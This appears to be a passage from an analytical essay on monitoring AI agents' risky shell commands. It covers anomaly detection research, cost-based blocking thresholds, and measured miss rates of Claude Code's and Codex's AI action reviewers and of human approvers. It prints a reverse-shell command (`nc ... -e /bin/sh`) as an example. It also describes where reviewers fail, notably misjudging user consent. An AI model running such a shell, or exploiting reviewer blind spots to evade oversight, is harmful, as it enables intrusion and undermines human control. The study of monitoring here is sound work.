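The steps before a short harmful action may help a monitor detect it, depending on why the agent takes the action. The PocketOS agent's search for a credential would have given a monitor evidence to combine before the final request. But an agent that wrongly believes a folder holds only its own edits may do nothing unusual until it runs `git reset --hard`. Its earlier steps then look like those of an agent in a clean folder, so their likelihood ratios are close to 1 and the monitor learns almost nothing by multiplying them.

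The weakest assumption is that the monitor's chances of catching each step are independent. If a monitor fails to recognise one dangerous use of a tool, it will probably miss the next nine as well. In the extreme case, where it catches either all ten steps or none, 50% recall on each step still gives only a 50% chance of detection. The lemma has versions for dependent steps, but the gain from each step can then be much smaller.

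### When weak evidence justifies a block

Precision matters most when a person has to investigate every alarm. An action reviewer must instead allow or block each action, and wrongly allowing one can have very different consequences from wrongly blocking one. Neyman and Pearson compared balancing two kinds of error to a court weighing the conviction of an innocent person against the acquittal of a guilty one. They wrote that mathematics can show how to control the two risks, but that the investigator must choose the balance between them based on the consequences.

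With a cost for each mistake, the choice becomes a short calculation. Let p be the probability that the action is harmful, given everything the reviewer has seen. C is the cost of stopping a harmless action, and L is the loss if a harmful action runs. Blocking has an expected cost of (1 − p)C, and allowing has an expected cost of pL. Blocking is cheaper when pL > (1 − p)C, which rearranges to

p > C / (C + L)

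If allowing a harmful command is as bad as blocking a harmless one, the reviewer should block when harm is more likely than not. If it is 999 times as bad, the reviewer should block whenever the probability of harm is above 1 in 1,000.

The hard reset described earlier is harmful 1 time in 5,000. If a harmful reset erases four hours of work and a false stop makes a developer spend one minute reading a prompt, L is 240 times C and the threshold is 1 in 241. The reviewer should allow the reset because its chance of harm is below that threshold.

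Now suppose the agent handles the block itself. It receives the refusal, runs the more cautious `git reset --keep` instead, and loses two seconds. A false stop wastes one-thirtieth as much time as before, so L is 7,200 times C and the threshold falls to 1 in 7,201. The reviewer should therefore block, even though the evidence against the command is as weak as before.

Over ten million actions, blocking every hard reset would cause about 100,000 false stops and prevent 20 losses of four hours each. If each stop took two seconds, the delays would total about 56 hours, less than the 80 hours of work saved. If each took a minute, they would total nearly 1,700 hours. Precision is 0.02% in both cases, so an officer who had to investigate every alarm would soon stop looking.

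The rule also supplies the threshold k that Neyman and Pearson left open. A reviewer should block when

Λ(x) > (C / L) × (1 − π) / π

With two seconds weighed against a four-hour loss and a base rate of 1 in 100,000, the right-hand side is about 14. If every harmful action causes the same four-hour loss, the reviewer should block `git reset --hard`, which has a ratio of 20, and allow `git push`, which has a ratio of 3. But a leaked customer list can do far more harm than four hours of lost work, and a high enough L would justify blocking the push too.

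If L is very large, the rule stops being useful because a reviewer that followed it would block every action. When the loss is ten million times as bad as a false stop, for example, the threshold is about 1 in 10 million, and even the commands under "everything else" in the table exceed it. The reviewer would need better evidence, or somebody would have to reduce what the agent's account can destroy.

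C also varies. A single refusal may take only two seconds, but Claude Code turns to a human after repeated blocks, so a reviewer that blocks freely will soon take up a person's time. Some tasks have no safer route, so a false stop prevents the agent from finishing them. The calculation also assumes that a block prevents the loss. An agent that rewords the same command and tries again gives the reviewer another chance to miss it, so a quick retry justifies blocking only if the agent's next action is likely to be safer.

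### Distinctive tokens

In these results, how much a monitor can learn from a command depends on how much more often its text occurs in harmful use than in harmless use, not on its length. A single token can determine that ratio. `rm -rf ~` and `git push` are equally long, but their likelihood ratios in the table of invented numbers are 100,000 and 3.

The likelihood ratio of a text is the product of its tokens' likelihood ratios, each conditioned on the tokens before it. A token that is equally likely at that point in harmful and harmless commands has a ratio of 1, so even a thousand such tokens add no evidence. There is no upper limit on how much evidence one token can add. In the command that erased a home directory in December 2025, nearly all the evidence was in the final `~/`.

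Longer text gives a distinctive token more places to appear, which puts short commands at a disadvantage. Very high ratios are also hard to establish. Even if a command never appears in a million harmless actions, its true share of such actions could be as high as about 3 in a million (the usual 95% limit), and harmful examples are scarcer still. The ratio also depends on the setting as well as the command. On disposable test machines that people wipe all day, `rm -rf ~` may be routine and its ratio close to 1.

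The Prisma command that emptied a live database was much longer than `rm -rf ~`, but it contained little that a monitor could flag without information about which database the address in the command pointed to.

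## Can anomaly detection pick out a harmful command?

Anyone who runs AI agents soon has a record of many thousands of harmless commands and very few harmful ones. Anomaly detection suits this imbalance because it needs no examples of harm. It learns what normal activity looks like and flags whatever departs from it. Security researchers have tried it on typed commands since the 1990s, mostly to catch people misusing computer accounts. It has worked moderately well on long stretches of an intruder's activity, but on single commands it mostly flags harmless oddities.

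### Scoring a command by its rarity

A detector of this kind first estimates, from past records, how often each command occurs in normal use. Call that estimate Q(x), as in the likelihood ratio. It then gives every new command a score that rises as the command gets rarer, for example

s(x) = −log₂ Q(x)

A command that makes up 10% of normal actions scores about 3.3 bits, one that makes up 1% scores 6.6, and one that occurs once in a million actions scores about 20. The operator sets an alarm threshold, often at the 99th percentile of the scores of normal commands that the detector did not learn from. If future normal commands resemble past ones, about 1% of them will set off an alarm.

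Counting exact commands often fails, because many contain a file name or address that has never occurred before. Detectors therefore count smaller pieces, such as words or pairs of words. They can also convert a command into an embedding, a list of numbers that is similar for similar texts, and measure how far it is from the embeddings of usual commands.

A classifier, by contrast, learns from examples labelled harmful or harmless, so it can estimate the whole likelihood ratio P(x)/Q(x), while an anomaly detector estimates only the denominator. Ranking commands by rarity would be sure to match the order given by Neyman and Pearson's best rule if every command were equally common among harmful actions, but some are far more common than others. In the invented figures used earlier, `rm -rf ~` made up one in a million harmless actions, so it scores 20 bits. A harmless `mv` command that moves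 a long list of files and occurs once in ten million actions scores 23, so a detector that flags `rm -rf ~` must flag the `mv` command too.

The classifier may miss a kind of harm that nobody has labelled, whereas an anomaly detector can flag such harm if it looks unusual.

### Impostors at the keyboard

The best-known experiments tried to detect impostors, people working in somebody else's account. Schonlau, DuMouchel and colleagues (*Computer Intrusion*, 2001) recorded 15,000 commands from each of about 70 Unix users. For privacy, they kept only the command names. The line `chmod +777 myfile`, which lets every user of the machine read, change and run a file, became `chmod`.

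Fifty of the users served as victims and the rest as impostors. Each victim's first 5,000 commands supplied the profile of normal behaviour. The researchers inserted stretches of an impostor's commands among the later ones, and the people running the detectors did not know where. The detectors classified each block of 100 commands as a whole.

The comparison covered six methods. One, called uniqueness, looked for commands that the victim had never used and gave more weight to those that few other users had used. Some methods examined which command followed which. Another tested how well a block compressed when added to the victim's history, on the theory that a person's new commands repeat patterns from their old ones. The table gives results for three of the six methods and for two later ones tested on the same data.

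| Method | Recall | False-positive rate |
|---|---|---|
| Uniqueness | 39.4% | 1.4% |
| Order of commands (Bayes one-step Markov) | 69.3% | 6.7% |
| Compression | 34.2% | 5.0% |
| Naive Bayes, with updating | 61.5% | 1.3% |
| Naive Bayes that can revise its scores | 75.0% | 1.3% |

Four of the original methods, including the three in the table, aimed for a 1% false-positive rate, but none achieved it. The test was deliberately hard, because the impostors were ordinary users doing ordinary work. A real intruder might behave more strangely.

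The detectors caught more intrusions when they had more commands to examine. At a 1% false-positive rate, most methods caught between 15% and 30% of the intrusions after the first block and 40% to 50% after about ten blocks, or a thousand commands. The researchers had also tried blocks of 500 and 1,000 commands in earlier runs and found that longer blocks separated users somewhat better.

A short harmful action would have gone unnoticed in such a block. The uniqueness score is an average over the 100 commands, and a command that is new to the user can add at most 0.01 to it. The threshold was 0.2319, so a block needed at least 24 new commands to set off an alarm. One destructive command among 99 familiar ones could not do so. Recording only command names made detection even harder, since `rm -rf ~` would have appeared as `rm`, which nearly everyone uses.

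Maxion and Townsend (2004), in *Masquerade detection augmented with error analysis*, reported 61.5% recall on the same data, a 56% relative improvement over the 39.4% achieved with uniqueness at about the same false-positive rate. Their naive Bayes classifier compared how often the victim and the other users typed each command, and it treated the commands as independent. They also obtained encouraging results with only ten commands at a time, which they considered more realistic. The version with 75% recall, which another researcher built later, can reclassify a block after processing the ones that follow. That helps find an intruder who is still logged in, but it cannot undo a command that has already deleted a folder.

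These classifiers learned from other users' commands as well as the victim's, so they aren't pure anomaly detectors. This may not matter much here, since *A Survey of Insider Attack Detection Research* (Ben Salem, Hershkop and Stolfo) describes an experiment in which detectors that learned from the victim's commands alone did about as well.

### Putting the arguments back

In *Masquerade detection using enriched command lines*, Maxion (2003) later tested whether the missing arguments had held detection back. He used an older collection of Unix commands that had kept the full lines, and ran the same type of classifier on the data twice, once with flags and arguments and once with only the command names.

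According to Ben Salem and colleagues, using full command lines instead of bare command names raised recall by more than 15% and the false-positive rate by about 21%. These look like relative increases. A detector with 60% recall and 5% false positives, for example, would move to about 69% and 6%. A laxer threshold could have produced a similar change, so these two numbers alone don't show which version was better. Comparing them requires plotting recall against the false-positive rate across the whole range of thresholds. The curve for full lines lay above the curve for bare names, so the extra text helped.

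That result fits the rule that more information can make better detection possible. But Maxion was measuring how well the text identifies its author. Habitual flags and familiar file names are good evidence of who is typing and much weaker evidence of whether a particular deletion is a mistake.

The benchmark also had faults that make its exact percentages doubtful. Ben Salem and colleagues explain that the recording system logged each command when its program ended, not when the user typed it, which corrupts the data for any method that relies on command order. Nobody knew whether the users had similar jobs, and some produced their 15,000 commands in days while others took months.

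A later study, *Masquerade Attack Detection Using a Search Behavior Modeling Approach*, used broad types of activity instead of exact commands and modelled how people search for files. An impostor who does not know where things are has to look around. The study's detector caught every impostor with a false-positive rate of 1.4%, on data its researchers had collected themselves. Its success depends on the impostor having to search, which an agent does not need to do if it already knows the path to a production database.

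### Language models trained on command lines

By the 2020s, researchers could train a language model on commands the same way they train one on English. The model predicts hidden tokens in a command from the tokens around them. It thereby learns which flags go with which programs, and it can produce embeddings for new commands.

Liu and Buford (2023), in *Anomaly Detection of Command Shell Sessions based on DistilBERT*, trained a small DistilBERT model on 1.15 million sessions from more than 15,000 users at a large enterprise. A session is everything a person types between logging in and logging out. Four standard outlier detectors scored each session's embedding, and the average was the session's anomaly score. High scores picked out some cases that the existing rules had missed, but also picked out maintenance work. One of the paper's three examples, which scored more than three standard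 deviations above average, was an administrator wiping disks before installing software on a set of machines. Liu and Buford concluded that a high score doesn't always indicate suspicious activity and recommended using the scores to decide which sessions experts should look at first.

They also trained classifiers, the best of which reached 79% precision and 99% recall. Those scores are less impressive than they look, because the classifier mainly had to reproduce the list of keywords, such as `ping`, `sudo` and `curl`, that the researchers used to label the sessions. A session counted as abnormal if it contained at least three different keywords and as normal if it contained none. Sessions with one or two were left out. Since `rm` is not on the list, a session consisting only of `rm -rf ~` would have counted as normal.

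Lin, Guo and Chen (2024) ran a larger experiment on individual command lines in *Intrusion Detection at Scale with the Assistance of a Command-line Language Model*. They collected 30 million training lines and 10 million test lines from a commercial cloud service with about 100,000 machines, and first tried anomaly detection without labels. A command that scanned every port of a network address, a typical preparation for an attack, had one of the ten highest scores out of ten million. But `mv` commands with many complicated file names and `echo` commands that only printed long, strange text also scored high.

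The team then trained the model further with labels from a commercial intrusion detector. They set the threshold low enough to catch nearly everything the detector had caught, and checked the extra alarms. About 83% of these were real intrusions that the detector had missed. The true recall is unknown because the count excludes intrusions that both systems missed. The team also removed duplicate commands before testing, so the precision applies to distinct commands, not to the stream of actions a monitor would face.

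Some of the remaining errors came from judging each line separately. One command might download a file and save it under the name `python`, and the next might run `python`. Each looks fairly innocent alone. When the classifier read three consecutive lines, the precision of its top 1,000 extra alarms rose from 94.9% to 99.8%. If a harmful action fits in one line, this added context helps detect it only when the lines before it are suspicious too.

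### Most unusual commands are harmless

The security company Sophos gave up on using rarity to find malicious commands. In *Sophos AI at Black Hat USA ’25*, Gelman and Bergeron ran three anomaly detectors on about 50 million distinct command lines a day throughout January 2025. They then had OpenAI's language model o3-mini label the anomalies as harmless or malicious. When human analysts checked a week's worth of labels, nearly all the "harmless" ones were correct.

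The anomalies were useful as training data instead. Companies usually choose common, simple commands as examples of harmless ones, because those are easy to label in bulk. This training data includes hardly any rare but legitimate commands, so a classifier trained on it tends to label them as attacks. Gelman and Bergeron therefore added the harmless anomalies to the training data.

The area under the curve (AUC) is the probability that a classifier gives a randomly chosen malicious command a higher score than a randomly chosen harmless one, so 0.5 is guessing and 1 is perfect. On commands from real investigations that experts had labelled, the AUC of the more sophisticated classifier rose from 0.61 to 0.89. A simpler classifier, whose original labels came from fixed text patterns, improved only from 0.71 to 0.77. With a procedure that used fewer resources and sampled 4 million lines a day,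 the simpler classifier did not improve noticeably.

The same experiment shows that the choice of test data can make the problem look solved when it isn't. The classifier that scored 0.61 on the experts' cases scored 0.998 on commands from the three weeks after its training period, before any anomalies were added.

Google's engineers also combined a broad search with a classifier, but the search looked for particular text rather than rarity. *Democratizing ML for Enterprise Security* (Momeni, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) describes a system for finding reverse shells, which are commands that connect a machine to an attacker's computer and let the attacker type commands on it. Deliberately loose rules search as many as 250 billion events a day for anything that resembles a reverse shell. A classifier then removes most of the false alarms, using a threshold based on how many cases people have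 time to investigate.

A harmful command can be hard to pick out because it may use the same program as a harmless one. For example, `nc 10.1.1.1 80 -e /bin/sh` uses the network tool `nc` to connect to another machine and give it a command line, while `nc -6 -vz -w 10 test.host 22` only checks whether a machine responds. Both open a connection, but the first is harmful because of `-e /bin/sh`, a few characters that a simple text model can learn to recognize.

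That may be why models that count short sequences of words did as well as models based on embeddings, a result the researchers had not expected. If the evidence lies in particular words, counting them is enough, and a more sophisticated reading adds little. The finding concerns commands whose text contains the evidence. Both types of model fail on a command like `git push`, because its text is the same whether it is harmful or harmless.

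### Attacks with ordinary tools

Some attackers use programs already on the machine instead of bringing their own, a practice known as living off the land. This is the closest parallel in the security literature to an agent's short harmful actions, because administrators run the same programs every day. For example, administrators use the Windows tool `ntdsutil` to take a snapshot of a company's directory of accounts in case of a disaster, but intruders use it to take the same snapshot and steal passwords.

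In *SENTINEL*, Shoeb, Hasan and colleagues (2026) built a detector for such attacks and tested it on 100 commands. Fifty came from published reports on Volt Typhoon, a Chinese state-sponsored campaign that stayed hidden in American infrastructure for over 18 months. The other fifty were harmless commands from company logs that used the same tools and a similar number of arguments. SENTINEL caught 47 of the 50 attacks and wrongly flagged 5 of the 50 harmless commands.

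That is good recall, though with only 50 attacks the true figure could plausibly be anywhere from about 84% to 98%. The 10% false-positive rate is a bigger obstacle. An agent that administers Windows machines would set off an alarm on about one in ten commands of this type, and nearly all of those alarms would be false.

Older methods did far worse. BERT, a standard language model, correctly classified 99.3% of the commands in an ordinary validation set but caught only 58% of the Volt Typhoon attacks. A simple word-counting method caught half. Shoeb and colleagues attribute this to the training data, in which harmless commands outnumbered malicious ones by 15 to 1, so a model could score well while missing the attacks.

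The imbalance explains only part of the drop. The validation set had 1,058 commands, about 65 of them malicious, and BERT made seven or eight errors. Even if every error was a missed attack, it caught roughly 88% of the malicious commands. The training data contained no Volt Typhoon commands, so the fall from 88% to 58% must be largely because the attacks were new. A classifier for agents would face the same problem whenever agents found a new way to cause damage.

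SENTINEL also contains an anomaly detector, but removing it changed accuracy by only 0.4 to 0.6 percentage points. By comparison, a component that reads commands character by character, and so recognises disguised text, contributed 5.6 points. The researchers kept the anomaly score to bring strange commands to an analyst's attention.

### Language models as judges

A general-purpose language model can also judge logs without any training on them, using what it already knows about programs and attacks. *HIDBench* (Sun, Tian and colleagues, 2026) tested nine such models, including Claude Opus 4.6 and GPT-5.2, on records of programs, files and network connections from simulated attacks. The scores date from the spring of 2026, and newer models have since replaced several of the nine.

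The results depended heavily on how noisy the logs were. On the easiest of three data collections, the models averaged 89% precision with a false-positive rate of 0.008%. On the second, which had busier machines and more ambiguous attacks, precision averaged 61% and the false-positive rate was sixteen times as high. On the third, some models were cautious while others raised many false alarms, including Gemini 2.5 Flash, which flagged about 2.1% of harmless items.

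High precision sometimes came with very low recall. On one set of logs, every alarm GPT-4.1 raised was correct, but its Matthews correlation coefficient was only 0.25. This coefficient accounts for both false alarms and misses, and is 1 for perfect detection and about 0 for guessing. When there are no false alarms and harm is rare, it is roughly the square root of recall, so GPT-4.1 must have found only about 6% of what it was supposed to find.

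The benchmark was also easier in one respect than live monitoring, where the time of an attack isn't known in advance. To fit the logs into the models' input, the researchers kept only the logs from each attack and from equally long periods before and after it.

*Cybersecurity Detection Classification with Reasoning-enabled Language Models* (Khanna, Nandan and colleagues, 2026) describes a model trained at the security company CrowdStrike to decide whether alerts raised by other software are real threats. The model receives the command, the commands that led to it, and figures on how common the activity is. It reasons about each alert in writing before deciding. Its verdicts agreed with those of human analysts 82.6% of the time.

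For automatic use, the company cares more about high-confidence verdicts. The researchers used two weeks of alerts to choose a confidence threshold at which 98% of "harmless" verdicts were correct. The system could then close 65% of the harmless alerts unaided, compared with 22% for a model that gave a verdict without reasoning. But in the following week, only 90.8% of the "harmless" verdicts above that threshold were correct.

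Rarity was more useful here than in Sophos's work. An automatic optimiser searching for good instructions produced a set with fixed cut-offs, such as calling anything sufficiently common harmless. With those instructions, the untrained model reached about 87.5% accuracy on the validation data, almost as high as the trained model's later score. The researchers rejected these instructions as brittle and unhelpful to analysts. Still, the result suggests that rarity is more informative about an alert that is already suspicious than about a command picked from the whole stream. An agent's monitor could likewise use rarity as a second piece of evidence about a deletion or an upload.

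### Why length is no help

Some detection rules measure only the length of a command. Splunk's *Unusually Long Command Line* flags commands that exceed the average length on a machine by more than three standard deviations, on the reasoning that attackers often disguise their instructions in long strings of code. Splunk labels the rule experimental, leaves it off by default, and notes that some legitimate programs also start with long commands.

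A command shorter than average can never trigger a rule that flags unusually long ones. Suppose commands on a machine average 80 characters with a standard deviation of 60 (invented figures). A threshold three standard deviations above the average would be 260 characters. The request that deleted PocketOS's database had about 160, and the command that erased a home directory in December 2025 had 31. The rule also runs once an hour on commands that are at least ten minutes old, so it could not have stopped either one.

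Another Splunk rule, *Potentially malicious code on commandline*, used a text classifier to look for suspicious programming terms, and its alert message referred to commands longer than 200 characters. Splunk has since removed the rule because it no longer works with current Splunk software.

Flagging unusually short commands would not work either. With the same invented figures, three standard deviations below average is minus 100 characters, so no command would be flagged. A fixed limit of ten characters would flag `rm -rf ~`, but also `git push`, `ls` and a large share of the other commands people and agents type.

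An anomaly detector can be biased towards flagging long commands even if it wasn't designed to be. Liu and Buford found that anomaly scores tended to rise with the number of tokens and lines in a session, and that short sessions usually looked routine. A detector that scores text by its probability tends to give longer commands higher scores because it adds up the scores of their tokens. For example, forty predictable tokens at 1 bit each total 40 bits, while four surprising tokens at 5 bits each total 20.

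Dividing by the number of tokens removes this bias, because the short command then scores 5 bits per token and the long one scores 1. But it also pushes typos to the top of the list. Lin and colleagues had to filter out misspellings such as `dcoker` for `docker`, which are short, rare and almost always harmless.

### From human attackers to AI agents

None of these studies tested a detector on AI agents' commands, and their results apply only partly to agents. Most tried to detect an outsider using somebody else's account. Ben Salem and colleagues distinguish such impostors from traitors, who misuse their own access. They judged that command histories work well for detecting impostors but poorly for detecting traitors, who know the system and can keep behaving as usual. They also mention insiders who do damage by mistake.

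An agent that overreaches or makes a mistake resembles an insider. It uses its own account, and its harmful command may be one it runs every week, such as a `git reset --hard` that this time discards a user's edits. An agent under prompt injection is more like an impostor, since an outsider's instructions may send it to files and addresses it has never accessed.

It is also harder to establish what is normal for an agent. The detectors in the 2001 experiment needed 5,000 commands to learn one person's habits, while an agent may finish a job in a few hundred and then start on something unrelated. A profile of only the current job has too little data. A profile of all the agent's jobs has plenty, but it will include database migrations, bulk deletions and uploads, which are all normal in some jobs. `volumeDelete` would probably have stood out among the PocketOS agent's commands, but it would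 not stand out for an agent that deletes test databases every night.

A new model can change how every agent works at once. It may use different tools or combine several commands on one line, and a detector trained on the old model's commands would then raise alarms about harmless work. Retraining the detector on recent commands could fix this, but if those include harmful ones, the detector learns to treat them as normal. Schonlau and colleagues tried to prevent this by updating profiles only with data that had raised no alarm. For the compression method, this steadily narrowed the range of behaviour that counted as normal, until the detector began to flag ordinary variation as intrusion.

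Security classifiers also rely on signs that an attacker is hiding something, such as scrambled text, renamed programs and split-up suspicious words. An agent's mistakes will lack these signs. For example, an agent that confuses production with staging writes the same clear command it would have written for staging.

Agents have some advantages over people as subjects for anomaly detection. The application that runs their tool calls receives every command with its arguments, which Schonlau's team did not have. Many copies of the same model may also behave more alike than 50 people do, so a company could pool their records and learn within hours of an update what is normal.

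Anomaly detection is most likely to work on an agent with one narrow, repetitive job. Some early security research monitored a few system programs instead of people, because each program did a limited range of things in a stable way. An agent that only restarts a service and reads its logs is similar, so a deletion would stand out in its record. But a fixed list of the few commands the job requires would catch the deletion just as well, needs no training data, and can block it before it runs.

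## How well do people and AI reviewers judge single actions?

A fixed list of permitted commands is enough for an agent with one narrow job. A coding agent's work varies too much for a list to cover every command, so somebody has to judge the rest. Until recently, the user usually had to approve each risky command before it ran. Anthropic and OpenAI now offer a second AI model that reviews these commands instead.

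Anthropic reported in March 2026 that Claude Code users approved 93% of permission prompts, and by August they approved 97%. These rates alone don't show that people are careless, because if 1 prompt in 1,000 concerned a harmful action, a perfect judge who objected only to harm would approve 99.9% of them. Measuring judgement requires a test in which the harmful actions are already known.

### Claude Code's two-stage reviewer

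In Claude Code's auto mode, an action reaches the AI reviewer only if simpler rules have not already settled it. The agent can read and search files without review. It can also edit files inside the project folder, because the user can inspect those edits later through version control. The reviewer judges most other actions, including shell commands, web requests and file operations outside the project.

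The reviewer was Claude Sonnet 4.6 when Anthropic described the design on 25 March 2026. Its prompt contains rules about what to block, a few exceptions, and instructions for working out what the user has authorised. Anything the agent chose by itself counts as unauthorised until the user says otherwise, and a question such as "can we fix this?" does not count as an order.

Claude Code's review has two stages, a quick check and a careful check. In the quick check, a model reads the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, then produces a single token, yes to block or no to allow. It is instructed to block when in doubt. Most actions pass and run at once. If the quick check flags an action, the same model reads the same input again, with an instruction to reason before deciding. Claude Code blocks the action only if both checks flag it. Using two stages saves money because the model generates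 reasoning tokens only for the few actions that the quick check flags.

Anthropic tested the reviewer on three sets of actions:

| Test set | Error | Quick check alone | Both checks |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10,000 real tool calls from employees' sessions | False-positive rate | 8.5% | 0.4% |
| 52 real cases of overreach | Miss rate | 6.6% | 17% |
| 1,000 synthetic exfiltration attempts | Miss rate | 1.8% | 5.7% |

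Out of 10,000 ordinary calls, the quick check alone would have stopped about 850. Adding the careful check reduced that to about 40 but also raised the miss rate. The careful check reviews only actions that the quick check flagged, so it can release harmful ones but cannot catch any that the quick check missed.

Adding the second check catches less overreach but makes a flag much stronger evidence of it. The quick check alone flags 93.4% of overreach and 8.5% of harmless calls, a ratio of about 11 to 1. With both checks, the rates are 83% and 0.4%, a ratio of about 200 to 1.

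The synthetic exfiltrations included uploads of sensitive data, pushes to untrusted remotes and passwords hidden in web addresses. The reviewer missed fewer of these than of the real overreach, even though many were disguised. One likely reason is that an upload to a stranger's server rarely resembles anything the user asked for, whereas an overreaching agent is trying to do the task the user gave it.

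The 52 cases came from sessions where an employee refused the action or somebody flagged it afterwards, so the set excludes harmful actions that nobody noticed. If the reviewer tends to overlook the same actions that people overlook, its true miss rate on overreach is higher than 17%.

### Recognising the danger but misjudging consent

In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the reviewer recognised that the command would delete something or overwrite a branch's history, but wrongly concluded that the user had agreed to it. For example, a user might ask the agent to "clean up the PR" (a pull request, or proposed set of changes to shared code), and the agent might respond with a force-push. The reviewer takes the request as permission because it is related to the action. In other cases, the user had approved a similar action earlier, and the reviewer treated that single approval as a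 general one. Anthropic tried to fix this by changing the prompt, but every change did more harm than good.

A reviewer can understand what a command does and still misjudge whether the user wanted it. Suppose a user says "get this branch back to a clean state" and the agent proposes `git reset --hard`. Even a reviewer who knows exactly which uncommitted edits the command would erase has to decide whether the user meant to give them up.

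*Ajar* (2026), a comparison of defences for AI agents, tested whether auto mode's verdicts depend on who gave the instruction. The researchers told an agent to make particular tool calls. Auto mode refused some of the calls when the instruction was in the system prompt, which holds the developer's standing orders, but allowed all of them when the same instruction was in the user's message. That is reasonable if the user wants the action, since a reviewer that overruled plain orders would be of little use. But a reviewer that reads too much into a user's words can end up providing no protection.

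Anthropic's current documentation, *Choose a permission mode*, now spells out what counts as consent: the user has to name both the action and the detail that makes it dangerous, such as the branch that a force-push would overwrite. Telling the agent "you can force-push" does not lift the block. An approval normally covers only one action. Under Anthropic's rules, the reviewer should never approve certain actions, including sending code or secrets to an outside party, so a user who wants that has to leave auto mode or run the command personally. The default reviewer is now Claude Sonnet 5, so the 17% miss rate describes an older model with older rules.

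### People at the approval prompt

Anthropic compared the reviewer with people before making auto mode the default in August 2026. It hired 1,053 professional testers through a research vendor and gave them coding work in an environment built for the study. Partway through each session, the text of one permission prompt changed to a clearly dangerous command, and the vendor recorded whether the tester approved it. The command did not run even if the tester approved it.

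The testers stopped 143 of the 1,053 commands (13.6%), and auto mode blocked 937 of the same commands (89%). Anthropic also published how often only one of the two stopped a command. The remaining numbers in this table follow by subtraction.

| | Auto mode blocked | Auto mode allowed | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tester refused | 137 | 6 | 143 |
| Tester approved | 800 | 110 | 910 |
| Total | 937 | 116 | 1,053 |

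The testers would have added little as a second check after auto mode. They refused only 6 of the 116 commands that auto mode allowed, so combining the two would have raised recall from 89.0% to 89.6%.

The testers also stopped fewer dangerous commands as a session went on, from about 17% early in the session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts. Auto mode's rate did not change with session length. Part of the testers' decline may come from differences between them, because those who click through prompts quickly reach the fiftieth sooner. Still, the decline fits what Axelsson expected of security officers who face mostly false alarms, since nearly all prompts are about harmless commands and are therefore false alarms to the user.

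The artificial setting could have made people look worse than they are. The testers were not working on their own projects and had nothing to lose if a command deleted the files, so they might have read less carefully than someone protecting a personal home directory. They knew that somebody was evaluating them, but not that the test concerned permission prompts. However, a developer who has answered such prompts every day for months might read less carefully than a tester in a single session.

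Every planted command was clearly dangerous, so the findings apply more to commands like `rm -rf ~` than to ambiguous ones like `git push`. Anthropic reported no false-positive rate for the testers, so it is unclear how much work their few refusals interrupted. Anthropic also had a commercial interest in the outcome, since it used the study to justify a change to its product.

Anthropic also examined real sessions from May and June 2026, all of which its safety systems had already flagged for review. An AI model graded the harm in each. Severe harm that the user had not explicitly asked for, on the scale of deleting rows from a production database, occurred in 6.3% of sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode. However, users chose their own mode, and some may have chosen manual approval because their work was dangerous, such as changing a production system. That would make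 manual approval look worse than it is.

People did much better in a smaller experiment. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026), 113 people from outside the software industry supervised a simulated assistant for a day of email, travel and shopping. The assistant attempted 18 actions, 7 of which went beyond what the user had requested. The 34 participants who had to approve or block each action blocked 59.6% of the overreaching actions and about 6% of the actions the task required.

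Several differences help explain the gap between 59.6% and 13.6%. Yan's prompts described each action in plain language, such as buying travel insurance for $12, while the testers had to read commands. There were only 18 prompts, and more than a third concerned overreach, so participants had little time to get bored and frequent reasons to object. The actions in Yan's prompts were also milder. Yan counted anything outside the assigned task as overreach, including a call to the airport to confirm a flight. Of the 34 participants, 30 allowed that call, and many of them may have thought it useful.

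Yan also tested a combination of AI and human review. For another 44 participants, Claude Sonnet 5 had selected in advance which actions needed a human decision. It selected all 7 overreaching actions and 3 of the 11 required ones. The participants made the final decisions and approved 46% of the overreaching actions, so the combined system stopped only 54% of them.

Letting people set rules beforehand did not help either. The remaining 35 participants chose "allow", "ask" or "never" for four kinds of action, such as spending money or deleting something. They chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, and when the assistant asked, they approved two-thirds of the overreaching actions.

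### OpenAI's Auto-review

OpenAI's coding agent, Codex, normally works in a sandbox that limits its access to files and network connections. It has to ask for permission to go beyond those limits. In April 2026 OpenAI introduced Auto-review, which sends these requests to a separate AI agent instead of the user.

*Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) illustrates the effect with 10,000 actions from use inside OpenAI. Of these, 9,280 stayed within the sandbox and ran without review. The reviewer approved 713 of the other 720 and denied 7. After four of the denials the agent found a safer way to continue, and after the other three it stopped and asked the user. Manual approval would have interrupted the user 720 times. The proportions depend on how a company configures its sandbox and what work its agents do.

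The sandbox therefore determines much of what the reviewer judges. By default, a `git push` to another machine needs network access, so it goes to the reviewer. A command that deletes an unfinished file in the project folder can run without review, because the agent already has permission to change files there. OpenAI's product documentation, *Auto-review*, lists this among the system's limits.

The reviewer caught 90.3% of synthetic cases of overreach, which covered unintended data transfers, weakened security and irreversible operations. It caught 99.3% of synthetic prompt injections that ran hostile code, stole secrets or uploaded data, but 90.2% when the team added categories such as destructive deletion and data tampering. Trębacz and colleagues explain that the reviewer allowed most of the additional cases because it judged the damage not serious enough. Researchers often agreed with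 it, so some of the measured misses are disagreements about what counts as serious harm.

The reviewer approved 99.1% of requests that users had approved in real sessions, which implies a false-positive rate of about 0.9% if the users were always right. Because people approve prompts so readily, a few of the reviewer's refusals may have been correct.

This 0.9% isn't directly comparable with Anthropic's 0.4%, because OpenAI's figure covers only requests to leave the sandbox, while Anthropic measured its rate on a sample of ordinary tool calls. The denials make up 0.07% of all 10,000 actions in OpenAI's illustration. Auto-review's 90.3% recall was measured on invented cases, so it doesn't show that Auto-review would beat the 83% that Claude Code's reviewer reached on real ones.

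AI control experiments test safeguards against models that might deliberately cause harm. In one such experiment, OpenAI's reviewer rejected at least one action in 96.1% of a hard set of simulated sabotage runs, though the rejected actions may not have included the harmful one.

### A test with ambiguous requests

*Measuring the Permission Gate* (Ji, Li and colleagues, 2026), a study from outside Anthropic, reported a far worse result for Claude Code's reviewer. Its test, AmPermBench, consists of 128 requests that make the user's aim clear but leave the limits vague. The requests cover four routine tasks: cleaning up branches, cancelling jobs, restarting services and removing old build files. Their wording varies in how precisely it identifies the target, how much the action could affect and how risky the setting is.

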